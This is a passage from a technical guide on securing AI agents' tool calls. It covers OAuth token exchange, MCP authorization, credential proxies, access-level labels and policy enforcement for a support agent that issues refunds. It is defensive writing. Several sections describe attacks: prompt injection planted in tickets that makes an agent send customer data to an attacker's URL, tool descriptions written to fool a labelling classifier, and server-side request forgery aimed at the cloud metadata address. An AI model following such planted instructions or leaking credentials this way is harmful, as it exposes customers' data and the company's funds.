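If the support agent hands work to a second agent, the new token can record both by placing one `act` field inside another. The outer field names the program now acting, and the inner fields name earlier ones. The standard requires a service to base its access decision only on the token's top-level fields and the current actor, so a rule such as "refuse refunds that began with the web-browsing agent" can't rely on the inner names.

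Support for these chains is also uneven. The standard has no common rules for extending and validating a chain over several exchanges, so *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Krishnan, Lopez and Addepalli, 2026) proposes six ways of handling chains. A second draft, the IETF's *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (2026), addresses the more basic problem that different systems represent the actor differently. A company that uses token exchange across several vendors' products should check that they all read `act` the same way.

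Token exchange also doesn't replace the separate record of where text came from that Surapani and colleagues want, because the dishonest refund request would arrive with a correct token.

### Audience restriction and token passthrough

Most access tokens are bearer tokens, which work for whoever holds them. The helpdesk service receives a token each time the runtime calls it. If the payments service accepted the same token, an attacker who compromised the helpdesk service could use it to issue refunds.

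Audience restriction prevents this. *Resource Indicators for OAuth 2.0* (RFC 8707, by Campbell, Bradley and Tschofenig) defines a `resource` parameter that a program sends to the authorization server to indicate where it intends to use a token. The server can then write that destination into the token's audience. If the helpdesk presents its token to the payments service, the service rejects it because the audience is wrong.

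A token can have several audiences, but Campbell and colleagues encourage requesting one audience at a time. Any service that receives a token with several audiences can use it at the others. Each scope also applies to every audience, so a token with `read` and `write` scopes for both helpdesk and payments covers all four combinations, even if the agent only needed to write to tickets and read charges. If one service hosts several customers or subsidiaries, the address in the `resource` parameter should include the part that identifies the intended one, so that the token fails at the others.

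Audience restrictions don't stop a thief from using a stolen payments token at the payments service. They also don't protect plain API keys, which have no audience field. The runtime has to restrict those keys itself by tying each one to a single destination.

Audience restriction also explains why a runtime shouldn't forward a caller's token to an API. The token Maria's agent presents has the runtime as its audience. Forwarding it works only if the payments service ignores the audience or accepts tokens meant for the runtime. In either case, the agent could send the token directly to the payments service and bypass the runtime's refund limit and log. If several services accept the token, an intruder in one of them can also use it to access the others. The Model Context Protocol guidance lists both problems among its reasons for forbidding the practice.

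### What the MCP authorisation rules require

Authorisation is optional in MCP, but under the specification of 28 July 2026 an implementation that supports it over HTTP takes on a substantial list of duties, set out partly in the main text and partly in the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026). The most relevant ones are:

| Requirement | Who must meet it | What it prevents |
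|---|---|---|
| Publish which authorization server issues tokens for this server | MCP server | Clients guessing where to log in |
| Name the target server in the `resource` parameter in both stages of a login | Client | Tokens that work at several services |
| Use PKCE, and stop if the authorization server doesn't advertise support for it | Client | Use of an intercepted login code |
| Check the issuer named in a login response before sending the login code anywhere | Client | Sending one issuer's code to a dishonest issuer |
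| Accept a return address only if it exactly matches a registered one | Authorization server | Sending a login code to an attacker |
| Accept only tokens issued for this server, and never forward them | MCP server | Reuse and passthrough of tokens |
| Keep tokens out of web addresses | Client | Exposure wherever software records addresses |

PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange) ties a login to the client that started it. The client creates a secret at the start, sends a value derived from it, and reveals the secret only when it collects the token. Someone who intercepts the login code can't use it without the secret.

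The issuer check has a gap because the specification only recommends that authorization servers name themselves in the response. If a server omits its name and hasn't advertised that it will include it, the client proceeds without the check. According to the specification, a later version is expected to require the name.

The 2026 text also deprecates dynamic client registration in favour of Client ID Metadata Documents. Dynamic registration would let an attacker register their own return address on most of the servers that Zhou and colleagues tested. With a metadata document, the client's ID is a web address where the authorization server finds a list of the client's return addresses. An attacker can still publish such a document, but it will be on the attacker's own domain, which the authorization server can show to the user or refuse. The protection is weaker for programs on the user's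 own computer, because the document can't prove which local program is waiting for the login code.

The Model Context Protocol recommends starting with few scopes and adding more when an operation needs them. The support agent could begin with permission to read tickets. When it first tried to issue a refund, the server would return a 403 naming the missing scope, and the agent would ask the authorization server for a new token. A client acting for a user should make this request, but a job acting for itself may stop instead, which is often better because nobody is there to judge the request. The security guidance also warns against treating a scope in a token as sufficient, so the server must still decide whether to allow the particular refund.

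These rules are stricter than common practice. WorkOS (2026), a company that sells login software, writes that implementers still widely omit the `resource` parameter and the server's audience check, although clients have been required to send the parameter since June 2025.

The specification covers the connection from the MCP server to the downstream API in much less detail. A server that calls such an API "may act as an OAuth client" to it, using a separate token issued by that API's authorization server. The specification doesn't prescribe a flow for obtaining this token, or explain how to choose between Maria's token and a service account, or how to protect an API key when the downstream service doesn't use OAuth. tianpan.co's *OAuth in MCP* (2026) points to an open request for MCP to support token exchange on a user's behalf, and describes companies as improvising in the meantime. Kumar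 and colleagues' claim that MCP leaves every detail of authentication to the implementer is nearly right for the connection to the API, though it is an overstatement for the connection between client and server.

Their gateway can get an employee's token for a downstream service either by sending them through that service's own login in the browser or by exchanging their SSO token without another login. The exchange is more convenient, but it only works if the downstream service's authorization server trusts the company's SSO. An outside payments provider usually won't, so a stored key remains the practical choice there.

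### Storing credentials and attaching them

Once the runtime has identified the caller and allowed the call, it looks up the secret for the logical name in its configuration, such as `vault/payments-key` in the DADL file shown earlier. How it attaches that secret depends on the API.

Dunkel includes five authentication schemes in DADL, which in his experience cover the vast majority of ordinary web APIs.

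| Scheme | What the runtime does for each request |
|---|---|
| Bearer token | Adds a stored token to a header |
| Basic | Combines a username and password, encodes them and adds them to a header |
| OAuth 2.0 client credentials | Uses an ID and secret to obtain a token, keeps it for later calls and renews it before it expires |
| Session | Logs in, extracts a token from the reply and logs in again if the API returns a 401 |
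| API key | Adds a stored key to a header or to the web address |

None of the five schemes involves an employee logging in. They suit service accounts, and Dunkel describes many users sharing one credential as the typical case in a company's tool library. Most calls therefore follow the flow where a user acts through a service account. The file identifies the right key for the payments API, but the runtime still has to check whether Maria may use it.

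Caching needs care for the same reason. Requesting a new token for every call would be slow and burden the authorization server, so the runtime keeps tokens until they are close to expiry. If it files Maria's mail token under "mail" alone, the next employee to call the mail API may get Maria's mailbox, recreating caller identity confusion inside the runtime. The runtime should file each token under the user, the API and the scopes. Model Context Protocol gives similar advice for other stored data, and adds that the user's ID should come from the verified token, not from a value the client supplies.

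Caching also delays the removal of access. If the runtime keeps Maria's token for an hour without checking it again, she may be able to use the mail API for up to an hour after the company disables her account. The company can shorten the token's lifetime, have the runtime check it with the authorization server more often, or have the runtime delete Maria's sessions and tokens when she leaves. The last option takes effect immediately for calls through the runtime.

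Some software won't start without an API key, but with a proxy that key can be a placeholder. OneCLI, an open-source credential gateway, lets the agent's software hold a string such as `FAKE_KEY` and send ordinary web requests. The gateway matches each request to a stored secret by its host and path, decrypts the secret and replaces the placeholder with it. Existing programs work unchanged, and an attacker who extracts the placeholder gets nothing of value.

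The agent still has to identify itself to the proxy. In OneCLI it does this with its own access token, so it still holds a secret. A thief could use that token to send requests through the proxy, within the agent's permissions. This is better than losing the payments key, because the company can revoke one agent's access without affecting anyone else.

Tuskira's AI Agent Gateway, another open-source product, requires each agent to send a gateway key and the name of a profile, which lists the tools the agent may use (Pogorelec, 2026). The gateway checks both before it fetches the real credential, and a refused call never reaches the API. But if an administrator hasn't tied the key to a profile, the caller can name any profile. Someone with a key leaked from a test machine could then choose the profile that allows refunds. Administrators can prevent this by binding each key to one profile.

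### One shared key or a token for each user

Where an API supports both, the company has to choose between one key for everyone and a separate token for each employee.

| | One shared key | A token for each user |
|---|---|---|
| What the API can enforce | The limits on the key | Each employee's own permissions |
| Who appears in the API's log | The company or service account | The employee |
| What one stolen credential exposes | Everything the key allows | What one employee's token allows |
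| Usage limits | All callers share one allowance | Depends on the API |
| Unattended jobs | Suitable | Unsuitable |
| Upkeep | One secret to replace | Many tokens to store, renew and revoke |

Per-user tokens give the company a second check. If a bug in the runtime lets Maria request a record she shouldn't see, the downstream service can still refuse. With a shared key, the service receives the same credential for every employee, so only the runtime checks what each employee is allowed to do.

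User tokens don't always give the agent narrower access than a service account, though. Maria may be able to read, delete and forward everything in her mailbox, and a token with broad scopes lets the agent do the same. A service account that can only send mail from one support address would be safer for routine replies. A store that holds tokens for every employee is also a valuable target, even if each token is worth less than the company's main key.

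The support agent would probably use both. If the helpdesk supports it, the agent could read tickets with a token for the employee on shift, so that the helpdesk applies that employee's permissions. For refunds, the runtime would first check the employee, then use a payments key that can only look up charges and issue refunds. The reconciliation job would have its own key that can only read charges. Giving the agent and the job separate keys takes little work and lets the company cut off one without stopping the other.

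Hiding either kind of credential from the model prevents the model from revealing it and stops an attacker from using it elsewhere or after the company has shut the agent down. As with the credential-only proxy, this wouldn't stop the dishonest refund.

### How a hidden credential can still leak

The secret has to leave the store to be used, and ordinary web software can then expose it in four main ways.

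| Route | How the secret escapes | Control |
|---|---|---|
| Redirects | An API sends the runtime to another address, and the runtime repeats the request there with the key | Turn off automatic redirects, or check each new address and remove the key when the host changes |
| Hosts chosen by the caller | A tool accepts a web address as an argument, and the runtime adds the key to a request to that address | Fix the permitted host for each credential in configuration |
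| Error messages | A failed request returns its own headers or address, and the runtime passes the text to the model | Return only an error code and a short message, and remove known secrets from responses |
| Logs | The runtime records headers, full web addresses or message bodies | Record the credential's name, and leave out its value |

An attacker can also use redirects and caller-chosen hosts to reach addresses inside the company's network, an attack called server-side request forgery. One target is the cloud provider's metadata address, usually `169.254.169.254`, which can return the machine's cloud credentials. For a shared runtime, leaking these could be worse than losing the payments key, because the runtime may use them to open the vault.

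The Model Context Protocol guidance covers this attack for the web addresses that clients fetch during an OAuth login, and the same controls make sense for tool calls. It recommends requiring encrypted connections, blocking private addresses and applying the same checks to every redirect. It advises against writing the address filter by hand, since attackers can disguise an internal address with an unusual encoding. They can also use a domain that points to a harmless address during the check and an internal one afterwards. An outbound proxy that blocks internal destinations when it connects handles both tricks better than checking the text of the address.

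DADL's fixed `base_url` helps here because the model supplies a charge ID, not a host. OneCLI matches secrets to hosts, which has a similar effect. That protection depends on how narrow the host pattern is, since a pattern that covers every subdomain of a large hosting service might include one that an attacker controls.

Default settings can reopen these routes. Tuskira's gateway always blocks the cloud metadata address and normally blocks private ones, but Pogorelec reports that its supplied set-up file permits connections to the host machine for local testing. Tuskira tells users to remove that exception on any shared system. The demonstration version also stores up to 1 MiB of each model request and response body, so the gateway records any secret pasted into a prompt until an administrator turns the setting off.

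Keys in web addresses are the hardest to keep out of logs, because servers and proxies routinely record the addresses they handle. MCP forbids this placement for its own tokens, but some APIs require it, so DADL and OneCLI support it. The runtime can remove the key from its own log but has no control over the provider's. If an API accepts its key in either a header or the address, the header is the better choice.

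## Labelling operations as read, write or more dangerous

When Maria's agent calls `issue_refund`, the runtime can identify the caller and the key to attach. It also needs a label giving the operation's access level, because rules that cover whole classes of operations depend on it. If the label is wrong, a sound rule produces the wrong decision.

### DADL's four levels

Dunkel defines the four standard values of a DADL file's `access` line as follows. The examples are from the support agent's company.

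| Level | Definition | Example |
|---|---|---|
| read | Retrieves data, with no side effects | Look up a charge |
| write | Creates or updates something | Add an internal note to a ticket |
| admin | Privileged operations | Let an employee issue refunds |
| dangerous | Destructive or irreversible operations | Delete a customer's record |

A company can also invent its own values, such as `billing`, `ops` or `pii` (personal data). DADL passes these through unchanged, and the company's policy determines how they are handled. A rule about `pii` then covers every operation with that label, including any labelled later.

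Dunkel's examples give each operation a single `access` value. If the field can hold only one, giving a customer look-up the custom label `pii` loses the information that it is a read. A misspelt `dangeruos` could also be accepted as a custom label that no rule covers. The company should keep a list of permitted values and reject any file that uses another.

The `access` line is also easy to miss. Dunkel Cloud's *DADL Specification v0.1* (2026), a draft from March, omits it from the table of tool fields, and the definitions above come from Dunkel's April paper. Someone who wrote files from the draft alone would probably leave every operation unlabelled.

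Dunkel describes the label as a contract between the file and the runtime's authorisation system. The file's author states what the operation does, and the company's policy determines who may use it. An author should label an operation that destroys data `dangerous` even if no current rule depends on it. DADL doesn't specify how to handle a wrong label, or a call that looks safe but becomes privileged with particular arguments, and leaves both problems to the runtime.

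### Why the HTTP method is a poor guide

A web request's HTTP method already labels it roughly. GET is meant for retrieving data, POST for submitting it and DELETE for removing it. Treating every GET as a read and everything else as a write would save a lot of work.

Dunkel gives two counterexamples to labelling operations by their HTTP method. `POST /search` is a read, and developers often use POST for searches because a complicated query doesn't fit well in a URL. `GET /admin/reset-cache` is dangerous despite being a GET. Under the HTTP standard, GET requests are meant to change nothing, but that depends on each API's developers following the standard.

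Labelling the cache reset as a read is a worse mistake than labelling the search as a write, because every agent with read access could trigger the reset and nobody would see a refusal. The other mistake would block or delay a harmless call, and someone would soon complain.

Reads sent by POST are not rare. The draft DADL specification includes an example in which a POST request fetches the status of a set of household devices. APIs built on JSON-RPC, the message format that MCP also uses, usually send every operation by POST to the same address, so the method does not indicate the operation's effect. DADL therefore infers no default level. An operation without an `access` line has no level, so the runtime needs a rule for that case.

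### How other systems label operations

MCP servers can attach optional hints, called tool annotations, to each tool. A March blog post by the protocol's maintainers lists the four behavioural hints and their defaults (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

| Hint | What it answers | If the developer omits it |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Does the tool leave its environment unchanged? | No |
| `destructiveHint` | If it makes changes, could they destroy something? | Yes |
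| `idempotentHint` | Is it safe to repeat the same call? | No |
| `openWorldHint` | Does it deal with outside people or systems? | Yes |

A client that follows these defaults treats an unlabelled tool as potentially destructive. The hints are also independent, so a tool can be both read-only and open-world, which DADL's standard levels can't express.

The server's developer sets the hints, and a dishonest developer can mark a tool that deletes files as read-only. The November 2025 specification (Model Context Protocol, 2025) therefore requires clients to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. During the review of the original proposal, the protocol's co-creator Justin Spahr-Summers asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued in the same discussion that clients should ignore annotations from untrusted servers. Under the final text,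 each client decides how much weight to give them.

The maintainers now separate hints from contracts. A hint is still useful if some servers get it wrong. They argue that a label belongs in the authorisation layer or the runtime if it must be true to be useful. So the support agent's company could use the annotations on a payments server that it wrote and reviewed itself, but it should assign its own labels to a server from a public registry.

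Few applications act on the hints. In *When Neither Side Confirms*, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026) used AI agents to trace the code of 41 open-source applications and development kits that call MCP tools. In 39 of them, marking a tool as destructive did not, by default, change how the software handled an ordinary call.

Honest developers can also interpret the same hint differently. *Tool Annotations*, from the sales-software company Outreach, marks every Outreach tool open-world because they all contact Outreach's own servers. On that reading, a look-up and an email to a stranger get the same hint. The maintainers acknowledge that "external" might mean outside the company's network or outside the local machine.

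An API's provider defines its OAuth scopes, and the API should refuse any call that the token's scopes don't cover, whatever the tool's developer wrote. But OAuth has no common list of scopes, so `read` can cover different operations at the helpdesk and the payments company.

Amazon Web Services (AWS) sorts the actions in its permission system into five access levels: List, Read, Write, Permissions management and Tagging. Amazon assigns the levels, and customers can use them to check what a policy grants. AWS puts deletion under Write, so creating and deleting a storage bucket have the same level, whereas the deletion would count as dangerous in DADL. AWS also has a level just for changing permissions, which would fall under DADL's broader `admin`.

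*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) describes a runtime guard that labels tools by effect, with classes such as `READ`, `COMMUNICATION`, `FINANCIAL` and `DELETE`. The agent sees a catalogue of tools that may contain descriptions written by third parties, while the guard uses a separate manifest of reviewed tools, fixed in advance, which also marks the arguments that need checking. A language model drafts the permissions for each task, but the guard overwrites any effect class the model proposes with the one in the manifest. If a server described its refund tool as a harmless look-up, the description might fool the agent, but the guard would still treat the call as financial.

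| Scheme | Who assigns the label | Who can rely on it |
|---|---|---|
| DADL access level | The author of the description file | The company's runtime, once someone has reviewed the file |
| MCP annotation | The server's developer | A client with good reason to trust that developer |
| OAuth scope | The API's provider | Any holder of the token, as far as the API enforces the scope |
| AWS access level | Amazon | AWS customers who write or check policies |
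| ToolFence effect class | Whoever reviews the manifest | The guard |

### Where a single scale breaks down

Dunkel suggests that a cautious runtime should apply the strictest label among operations that run together. This rule only makes sense if the levels are ordered, from read up to dangerous. A company can explain that order in a sentence and write short policies with it, but it handles several common cases badly.

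Outreach's documentation describes a read-only tool as "safe to auto-approve". Such a tool may be safe for the stored data, but using it can still cause harm. Looking up a charge puts a customer's payment record into the model's input, and reading a ticket adds text written by outsiders. An operation that lists API keys could give the agent a new credential. Some providers also charge for each look-up, so an agent stuck in a loop of reads can run up a bill.

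Labels can mislead even more when operations combine, as in the attack that uses a ticket, a payment record and an email. The software developer Simon Willison calls this mix of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out the "lethal trifecta". DADL labels both looking up a charge and reading a ticket as `read`, although the first returns private records and the second returns text that an attacker may have written. The MCP maintainers conclude that the risk of a tool such as `search_emails` depends on the other tools in the session.

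Nobody can reliably recall an email, so by Dunkel's definition sending one belongs at the top level, `dangerous`, along with deleting a customer's record. The support agent sends mail all day, so its policy would have to allow `dangerous` operations, and a rule based only on the level would let it delete records as well. Labelling mail as `write` avoids this but treats it the same as adding an internal note. It is also unclear why `dangerous` should always rank above `admin`, since giving the wrong person refund rights could do far more harm than permanently deleting a draft reply.

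Even reversibility covers several properties, and *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) argues that a single scale from reversible to irreversible can't capture them. Deleting a record is safe to repeat because the second deletion changes nothing. Adding €10 to a customer's balance isn't safe to repeat, but two such additions can happen in either order, unlike a deletion and an update of the same record. Whether an operation is safe to repeat matters when the payments API times out during a refund, because the runtime can't determine whether the money moved, and trying again may pay the customer twice.

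Undoing an operation may not undo its consequences. In one of Trofimov and Novikov's examples, a company withdraws an offer after a supplier has acted on it, and the withdrawal doesn't reverse what the supplier did. The support agent could likewise send a correction to a mistaken email, but the customer may already have relied on the original.

Several schemes therefore use separate labels. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) labels each tool by action type, data sensitivity and "externality", meaning whether the tool affects other people, money or the physical world. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026) labels each tool's object, action, sensitivity, privacy and integrity. In its example, a tool that reads a note is a low-sensitivity read, but its output is "unfiltered" because no trusted party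 has checked the note for malicious content. The support agent's runtime needs the same information about tickets.

MCP may move in this direction too. MCPProxy's *Deep Dive* (2026), a blog post from the makers of an MCP proxy, reports a proposal for three more hints, which would mark tools that access private data, tools that can send data out, and tools whose effects are reversible.

Separate labels take more work to assign, and each one adds a chance of error. A reasonable compromise is to keep DADL's level for broad rules and add labels for reversibility, data sensitivity and outside reach. The company can leave out any label that no rule would use. The MCP maintainers apply a similar test to proposed annotations, asking what a client would do differently if it had them.

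### When the danger depends on the arguments

A label belongs to an operation and covers every call to it, so `issue_refund` has the same label whether the refund is $5 or $50,000. There are three ways to deal with this.

A company can label each operation according to its worst case, marking refunds `dangerous` because of the largest refund the key permits. This is simple and safe, but a 5-dollar refund then gets the same treatment as a 50,000-dollar one. If every refund needs approval, employees may soon stop reading the requests.

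The company can split the refund operation into `issue_small_refund`, with a fixed limit of 50 dollars, and `issue_refund` for larger amounts, so that each can have its own level. This also works with a gateway that reads only the tool's name. The limit has to be in code that the model can't change, and someone should test it. DADL accepts validation keywords such as `minimum` in its type definitions but ignores them when it generates the interface that the model programs against, so an author shouldn't assume that a maximum written there will stop a large refund.

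ToolFence's manifest labels arguments that carry authority, such as the recipient and amount of a payment. The label shows which values need checking, and the policy sets the limit. For refunds, labelling arguments is usually the best choice if the policy engine can read them, because the company can change the limit without relabelling anything.

A limit on an amount also needs a currency and a unit. Some payments APIs take amounts in the currency's smallest unit, so `5000` could mean 50 dollars or 5,000 yen. The reviewer should record the unit next to the label.

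Other arguments matter besides amounts. An email that is routine when sent to the customer who opened the ticket may be a leak when sent to a stranger. The safety of a read also depends on its arguments. ToolFence lets some reviewed local reads run without further review, but only if all their arguments come from the user. Fetching a web address that the agent found on a page doesn't qualify.

MCP's annotations describe a tool in general and can't vary by call. The protocol's interest group on annotations is considering runtime annotations that would change this, according to its page on the Model Context Protocol site. A server might then mark a $50,000 refund differently from a $5 one, although a client would still need a reason to trust the server's label.

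### Ten operations of the support agent

The table labels the agent's four original operations and six others that the company might add. The levels follow Dunkel's definitions as written, and some are debatable.

| Operation | DADL level | Effect | Can someone undo it? | Data involved | Outside reach |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read ticket | read | Retrieves | Nothing to undo | Personal | Outsiders' text comes in |
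| Search tickets, sent by POST | read | Retrieves | Nothing to undo | Personal, from many customers | Outsiders' text comes in |
| Look up charge | read | Retrieves | Nothing to undo | Financial | None beyond the payments company |
| Add internal note | write | Creates | Yes | Whatever the agent writes | None |
| Send mail | dangerous | Sends | No | Whatever the agent writes | Text goes out |
| Issue refund | dangerous | Moves money | Not reliably | Financial | Money goes out |
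| Let an employee issue refunds | admin | Changes permissions | Yes, but not the refunds issued meanwhile | Staff accounts | None directly |
| Delete customer record | dangerous | Deletes | No | Personal | None |
| Open a link from a ticket | dangerous | Retrieves, but can also send | No, if data has left | Whatever the address contains | Both directions |
| Run a database query | dangerous | Depends on the query | Depends on the query | Anything in the database | Depends on the query |

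The last two are the hard cases. Opening a link to an arbitrary address can send data out, though a model or a hurried reviewer would probably label it as a read. An attacker could plant an instruction that makes the agent open an address on the attacker's site with a customer's details added to the end. The attacker's server would receive the details with the request, whatever page it returned. The label `read` would be fair if the runtime only opened links to a few fixed hosts that the company trusts.

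The database query can count open tickets or delete them all, so its safest label is `dangerous`. It would be better to replace it with several narrow operations, such as "count open tickets". Alternatively, the company could connect with a read-only database account. The database would then reject deletions, and the label `read` would be accurate, although the query could still return every customer's details. That label is correct only for that credential, so the company would need to review it again before switching to a broader one.

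The table also shows that the level alone leaves out a lot about an operation. Three operations are ordinary reads, but two of them bring in text from strangers and the other returns financial data. Five are dangerous, and the agent needs at least two of them, mail and refunds, for its normal job.

### How often labels are wrong

If each operation has one label and 2% of labels are wrong, a catalogue of 1,833 operations, the size of Dunkel's public registry, would contain about 37 errors. With four labels per operation and independent errors at the same rate, nearly 8% of operations, or about 142, would have at least one wrong label. The 2% rate and the independence of errors are assumptions, chosen to show that even careful labelling leaves errors in a large catalogue. The harm depends on the direction of the error. A search labelled as dangerous will annoy people until they correct it,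 but a deletion labelled as a read can go unnoticed until an agent uses it.

Tool authors often omit safety labels entirely. In *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, Afsar (2026) randomly sampled 400 servers from the locally run JavaScript packages in MCP's official registry. Only 195 started, and 58.8% of the 2,766 tools they offered had no safety annotations. Of the 194 servers with any tools, 72 annotated all of them and 122 annotated none. Authors seem to supply what MCP requires but often skip optional parts such as annotations, since none of the 2,766 tools had a fatal error in its schema, the required description of its arguments.

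Trofimov and Novikov queried the registry's remote servers instead and collected 98,291 tools. Only 26.0% had no annotation, but one publisher supplied 45.0% of the tools and set all four hints on every one. Without that publisher, 47.2% had no annotation. A hint may also have been filled in from a template, without anyone assessing that tool. Only 3.1% of all the tools were explicitly marked as destructive.

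It is harder to find out how often tool authors choose the wrong label, and the nearest measure comes from Yao and colleagues. They had language models classify a sample of tools from registry servers, with access to the source code, and found 269 destructive ones. They calculated that if every application asked for approval unless a tool's author had labelled it read-only or non-destructive, the tool would still run without approval in 5.4% of the pairings of an application with a destructive tool. That rises to at least 10.6% after adding destructive tools that the original search missed. Some of these labels may reflect differences of opinion rather than mistakes, since the models tended to count reversible actions, such as renaming a project, as destructive.

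Labels based on a tool's description inherit any errors in the description. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, used a language model to compare 19,200 tool descriptions with the tools' code and judged 9.93% inconsistent. Many of the inconsistent descriptions claimed more than the code did, which needn't affect the access level. Others do affect it, for example by omitting that the tool also changes stored data or sends it elsewhere. A reviewer who reads only the description would label such a tool `read`.

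### How well models assign labels

Language models are an obvious way to label a large catalogue, and Dunkel already drafts most of the registry's files with one. Yan tested this on 120 MCP tools, chosen to include ambiguous and high-stakes cases. Three people labelled each tool from its name, description and arguments, and agreed closely. Yan then compared four automatic methods with their consensus. "Main action" counts a result as correct even if secondary labels are missing or extra, as can happen with a tool that both reads and sends.

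| Method | Main action correct | Every action label correct |
|---|---|---|
| Language model | 90.0% | 72.5% |
| Keywords such as "delete" | 78.3% | 43.3% |
| Broad OAuth-style scopes | 75.8% | 16.7% |
| Copying the most similar tool's labels | 45.8% | 43.3% |

The model used instructions that Yan had refined on 20 of these tools. On the other 100, it again got 90.0% of main actions right, but it got the full set of action labels right for only 69.0% of tools. It did worse on data sensitivity (77.8%) than on externality (86.9%). The poor result for OAuth-style scopes shows how much detail reducing everything to read, write and admin loses, but it doesn't show that real providers assign their scopes badly.

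Yan also simulated a rule that banned one category of action at a time. With the model's labels, the rule let through 14% of the tools it should have stopped and blocked 4% of those it should have allowed. Having a person review the model's low-confidence answers reduced the 14% only to 11%, because most of the mistakes were high-confidence answers. If a catalogue of 1,833 operations had 200 destructive ones and a model missed 14% of them, 28 would have labels that were too mild. This estimate may be pessimistic, because an ordinary catalogue should have fewer hard cases than Yan's.

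Asking the model to label a tool more than once helps find the hard cases. Yan classified each of 20 selected tools ten times. The ten clear tools each got the same labels every time, while five of the ten difficult ones got different action labels between runs. But agreement between runs doesn't prove that a label is right, since a model can repeat the same mistake.

Other measurements are broadly similar. In *How are AI agents used?* (2026), a study of 177,000 MCP tools, human validators agreed with a model 81% of the time on whether a tool only perceives (such as reading a file) or acts (such as editing one). Yao and colleagues' models also had the source code, and the models agreed with two human annotators about whether a tool was destructive on 51 of the 56 tools that the annotators were sure about. In the other five cases the models were too cautious, which is the safer kind of error.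 Access to the code may partly explain the better result, but the two tasks differ too much to be sure.

None of these tests involved a tool description written to deceive the classifier. A model that labels a tool reads text supplied by the tool's author, so a malicious author can try prompt injection on the model too. Yan concludes that the classifier isn't reliable enough to be a security boundary on its own.

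### Reviewing labels

At two minutes per operation, one person would need about 61 hours to review 1,833 labels. That is manageable once, but a company that adds APIs every month needs to concentrate on the labels that could do the most harm if wrong. The following procedure does that:

1. **Draft the labels from the API's own documentation.** A model can do this, and should do it at least twice. The reviewer looks first at operations where the drafts differ.
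2. **Ask what the worst call could do.** The reviewer assumes that an attacker chooses all the arguments and that the runtime attaches the real credential. This catches the link and the database query.
3. **Get a second opinion on every `read` label.** A mistaken `read` is the costliest kind, because most policies will allow reads freely. The second reviewer shouldn't see the first label, and the stricter one applies until the two agree.
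4. **Test uncertain operations in a test account.** The reviewer calls the operation and checks whether any records changed, any mail went out or any charge appeared on the bill. A clean test doesn't rule out effects with other arguments.
5. **Save the definition with the label.** If the operation's address, arguments or description later change, the label lapses until someone reviews it again.

For the last step, the company has to keep its own copy of the definition. *Same Name, Different Server* (2026) examined all 72,606 version records in MCP's public registry and found no tool definitions, because the registry's format has no place for them. A reviewer therefore can't use the registry to check whether a tool has changed since the last review. A saved copy won't reveal a change to the server's code if the description stays the same, so the company should also fix the version of any server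 it installs. It can't do that for a remote server or an outside API, because the provider controls the code.

Checking a random sample works well for estimating how many errors remain, but not for finding them. If a reviewer checks 150 operations at random and finds no mistakes, the company can be about 95% confident that the error rate is below 2%, which still allows up to 37 wrong labels in the full catalogue.

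### A rule for unlabelled operations

The runtime should refuse to load an operation that has no label, so that its author sees the error while adding the API and can fix it before any agent depends on the operation. Afsar found that authors comply with the mandatory schema, which suggests that they would also fill in a mandatory label, though probably not always with much thought.

If the company can't refuse unlabelled operations, perhaps because it has put a gateway in front of 20 existing servers, it should give each such operation the strictest value of every label. The runtime would then treat the operation as dangerous, irreversible, and able to reach sensitive data and send it out. This follows Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, under which a system denies access unless someone has granted it. MCP's defaults are similarly cautious.

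By default, 60.7% of Yao and colleagues' pairings of an application with a destructive tool involved no enforced human approval. They calculated that this share would fall to 5.4% if applications asked the user about everything not annotated as safe. But among tools that had looked destructive and turned out not to be, the share of pairings in which the user had to answer a request would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%. People who get that many needless requests may start approving them without reading them.

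The strict default is therefore best as a temporary measure. The company can see from the runtime's log which unlabelled operations agents call most, and label those first.

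## Writing the policy and deciding each call

Access levels take effect only when a policy uses them and the runtime applies that policy to every call. The documentation for ToolMesh, the runtime built for DADL files, describes each step.

### One refund from request to record

Suppose Maria has the support agent work through her tickets, and the agent asks to refund $40 on charge `ch_4821`. In the sequence that ToolMesh describes, the call goes through seven steps:

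1. Authenticate: the runtime checks the caller's OAuth login or API key and finds the user, plan and roles that go with it.
2. Authorise: it asks OpenFGA, an open-source authorisation engine, whether this user may run this tool.
3. Fetch the credential: it looks up the payments key by its logical name.
4. Check the input: a JavaScript policy can examine the arguments, including the $40, and reject the call.
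5. Execute: the runtime sends the request to the payments API with the key.
6. Check the output: a policy can remove personal data from the response or withhold it altogether.
7. Record: the runtime logs the call and its result.

If any of the first four steps fails, the runtime fails closed, meaning it doesn't send the refund. ToolMesh also puts each caller in a class. A developer's laptop is typically `trusted`, while hosted agents and automated jobs are `untrusted`. A policy can block an untrusted caller from admin tools even if the user's plan includes them, so Maria's agent can have fewer permissions than Maria.

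The output check comes after the money has moved, so it can hide the payments company's reply but can't stop the refund. If the agent then receives only an error, it may retry the refund. The runtime should instead report that the refund succeeded and that a policy withheld the details. The runtime also records the call last, so a crash just after step 5 could leave a refund with no log entry. Writing a short entry before sending the request would avoid this.

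Automatic retries may also refund a customer twice. ToolMesh's sample DADL file sets the runtime to retry up to three times after certain server errors. The company should turn retries off for refunds unless the payments API can recognise a repeated request.

### When the policy engine doesn't answer

Older ToolMesh documentation describes a default mode with no authorisation checks. The current version, described in DunkelCloud's *ToolMesh*, checks every call by default. It runs OpenFGA inside its own process, so the checks don't depend on a network connection between the two. A company can instead use a separate OpenFGA server, which could become unreachable.

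ToolMesh's default for every uncertainty is "do not run". This should cover a policy server outage, but its examples are a refusal by OpenFGA, a rejection by the input check and a failure to fetch the credential. The *Fail-closed behavior guide* for another, smaller gateway covers an outage explicitly. If the gateway can't be reached or returns an error, the calling software treats this as a refusal and the tool never runs. A company that uses a separate policy server should test for this by stopping the server and requesting a refund in a test account.

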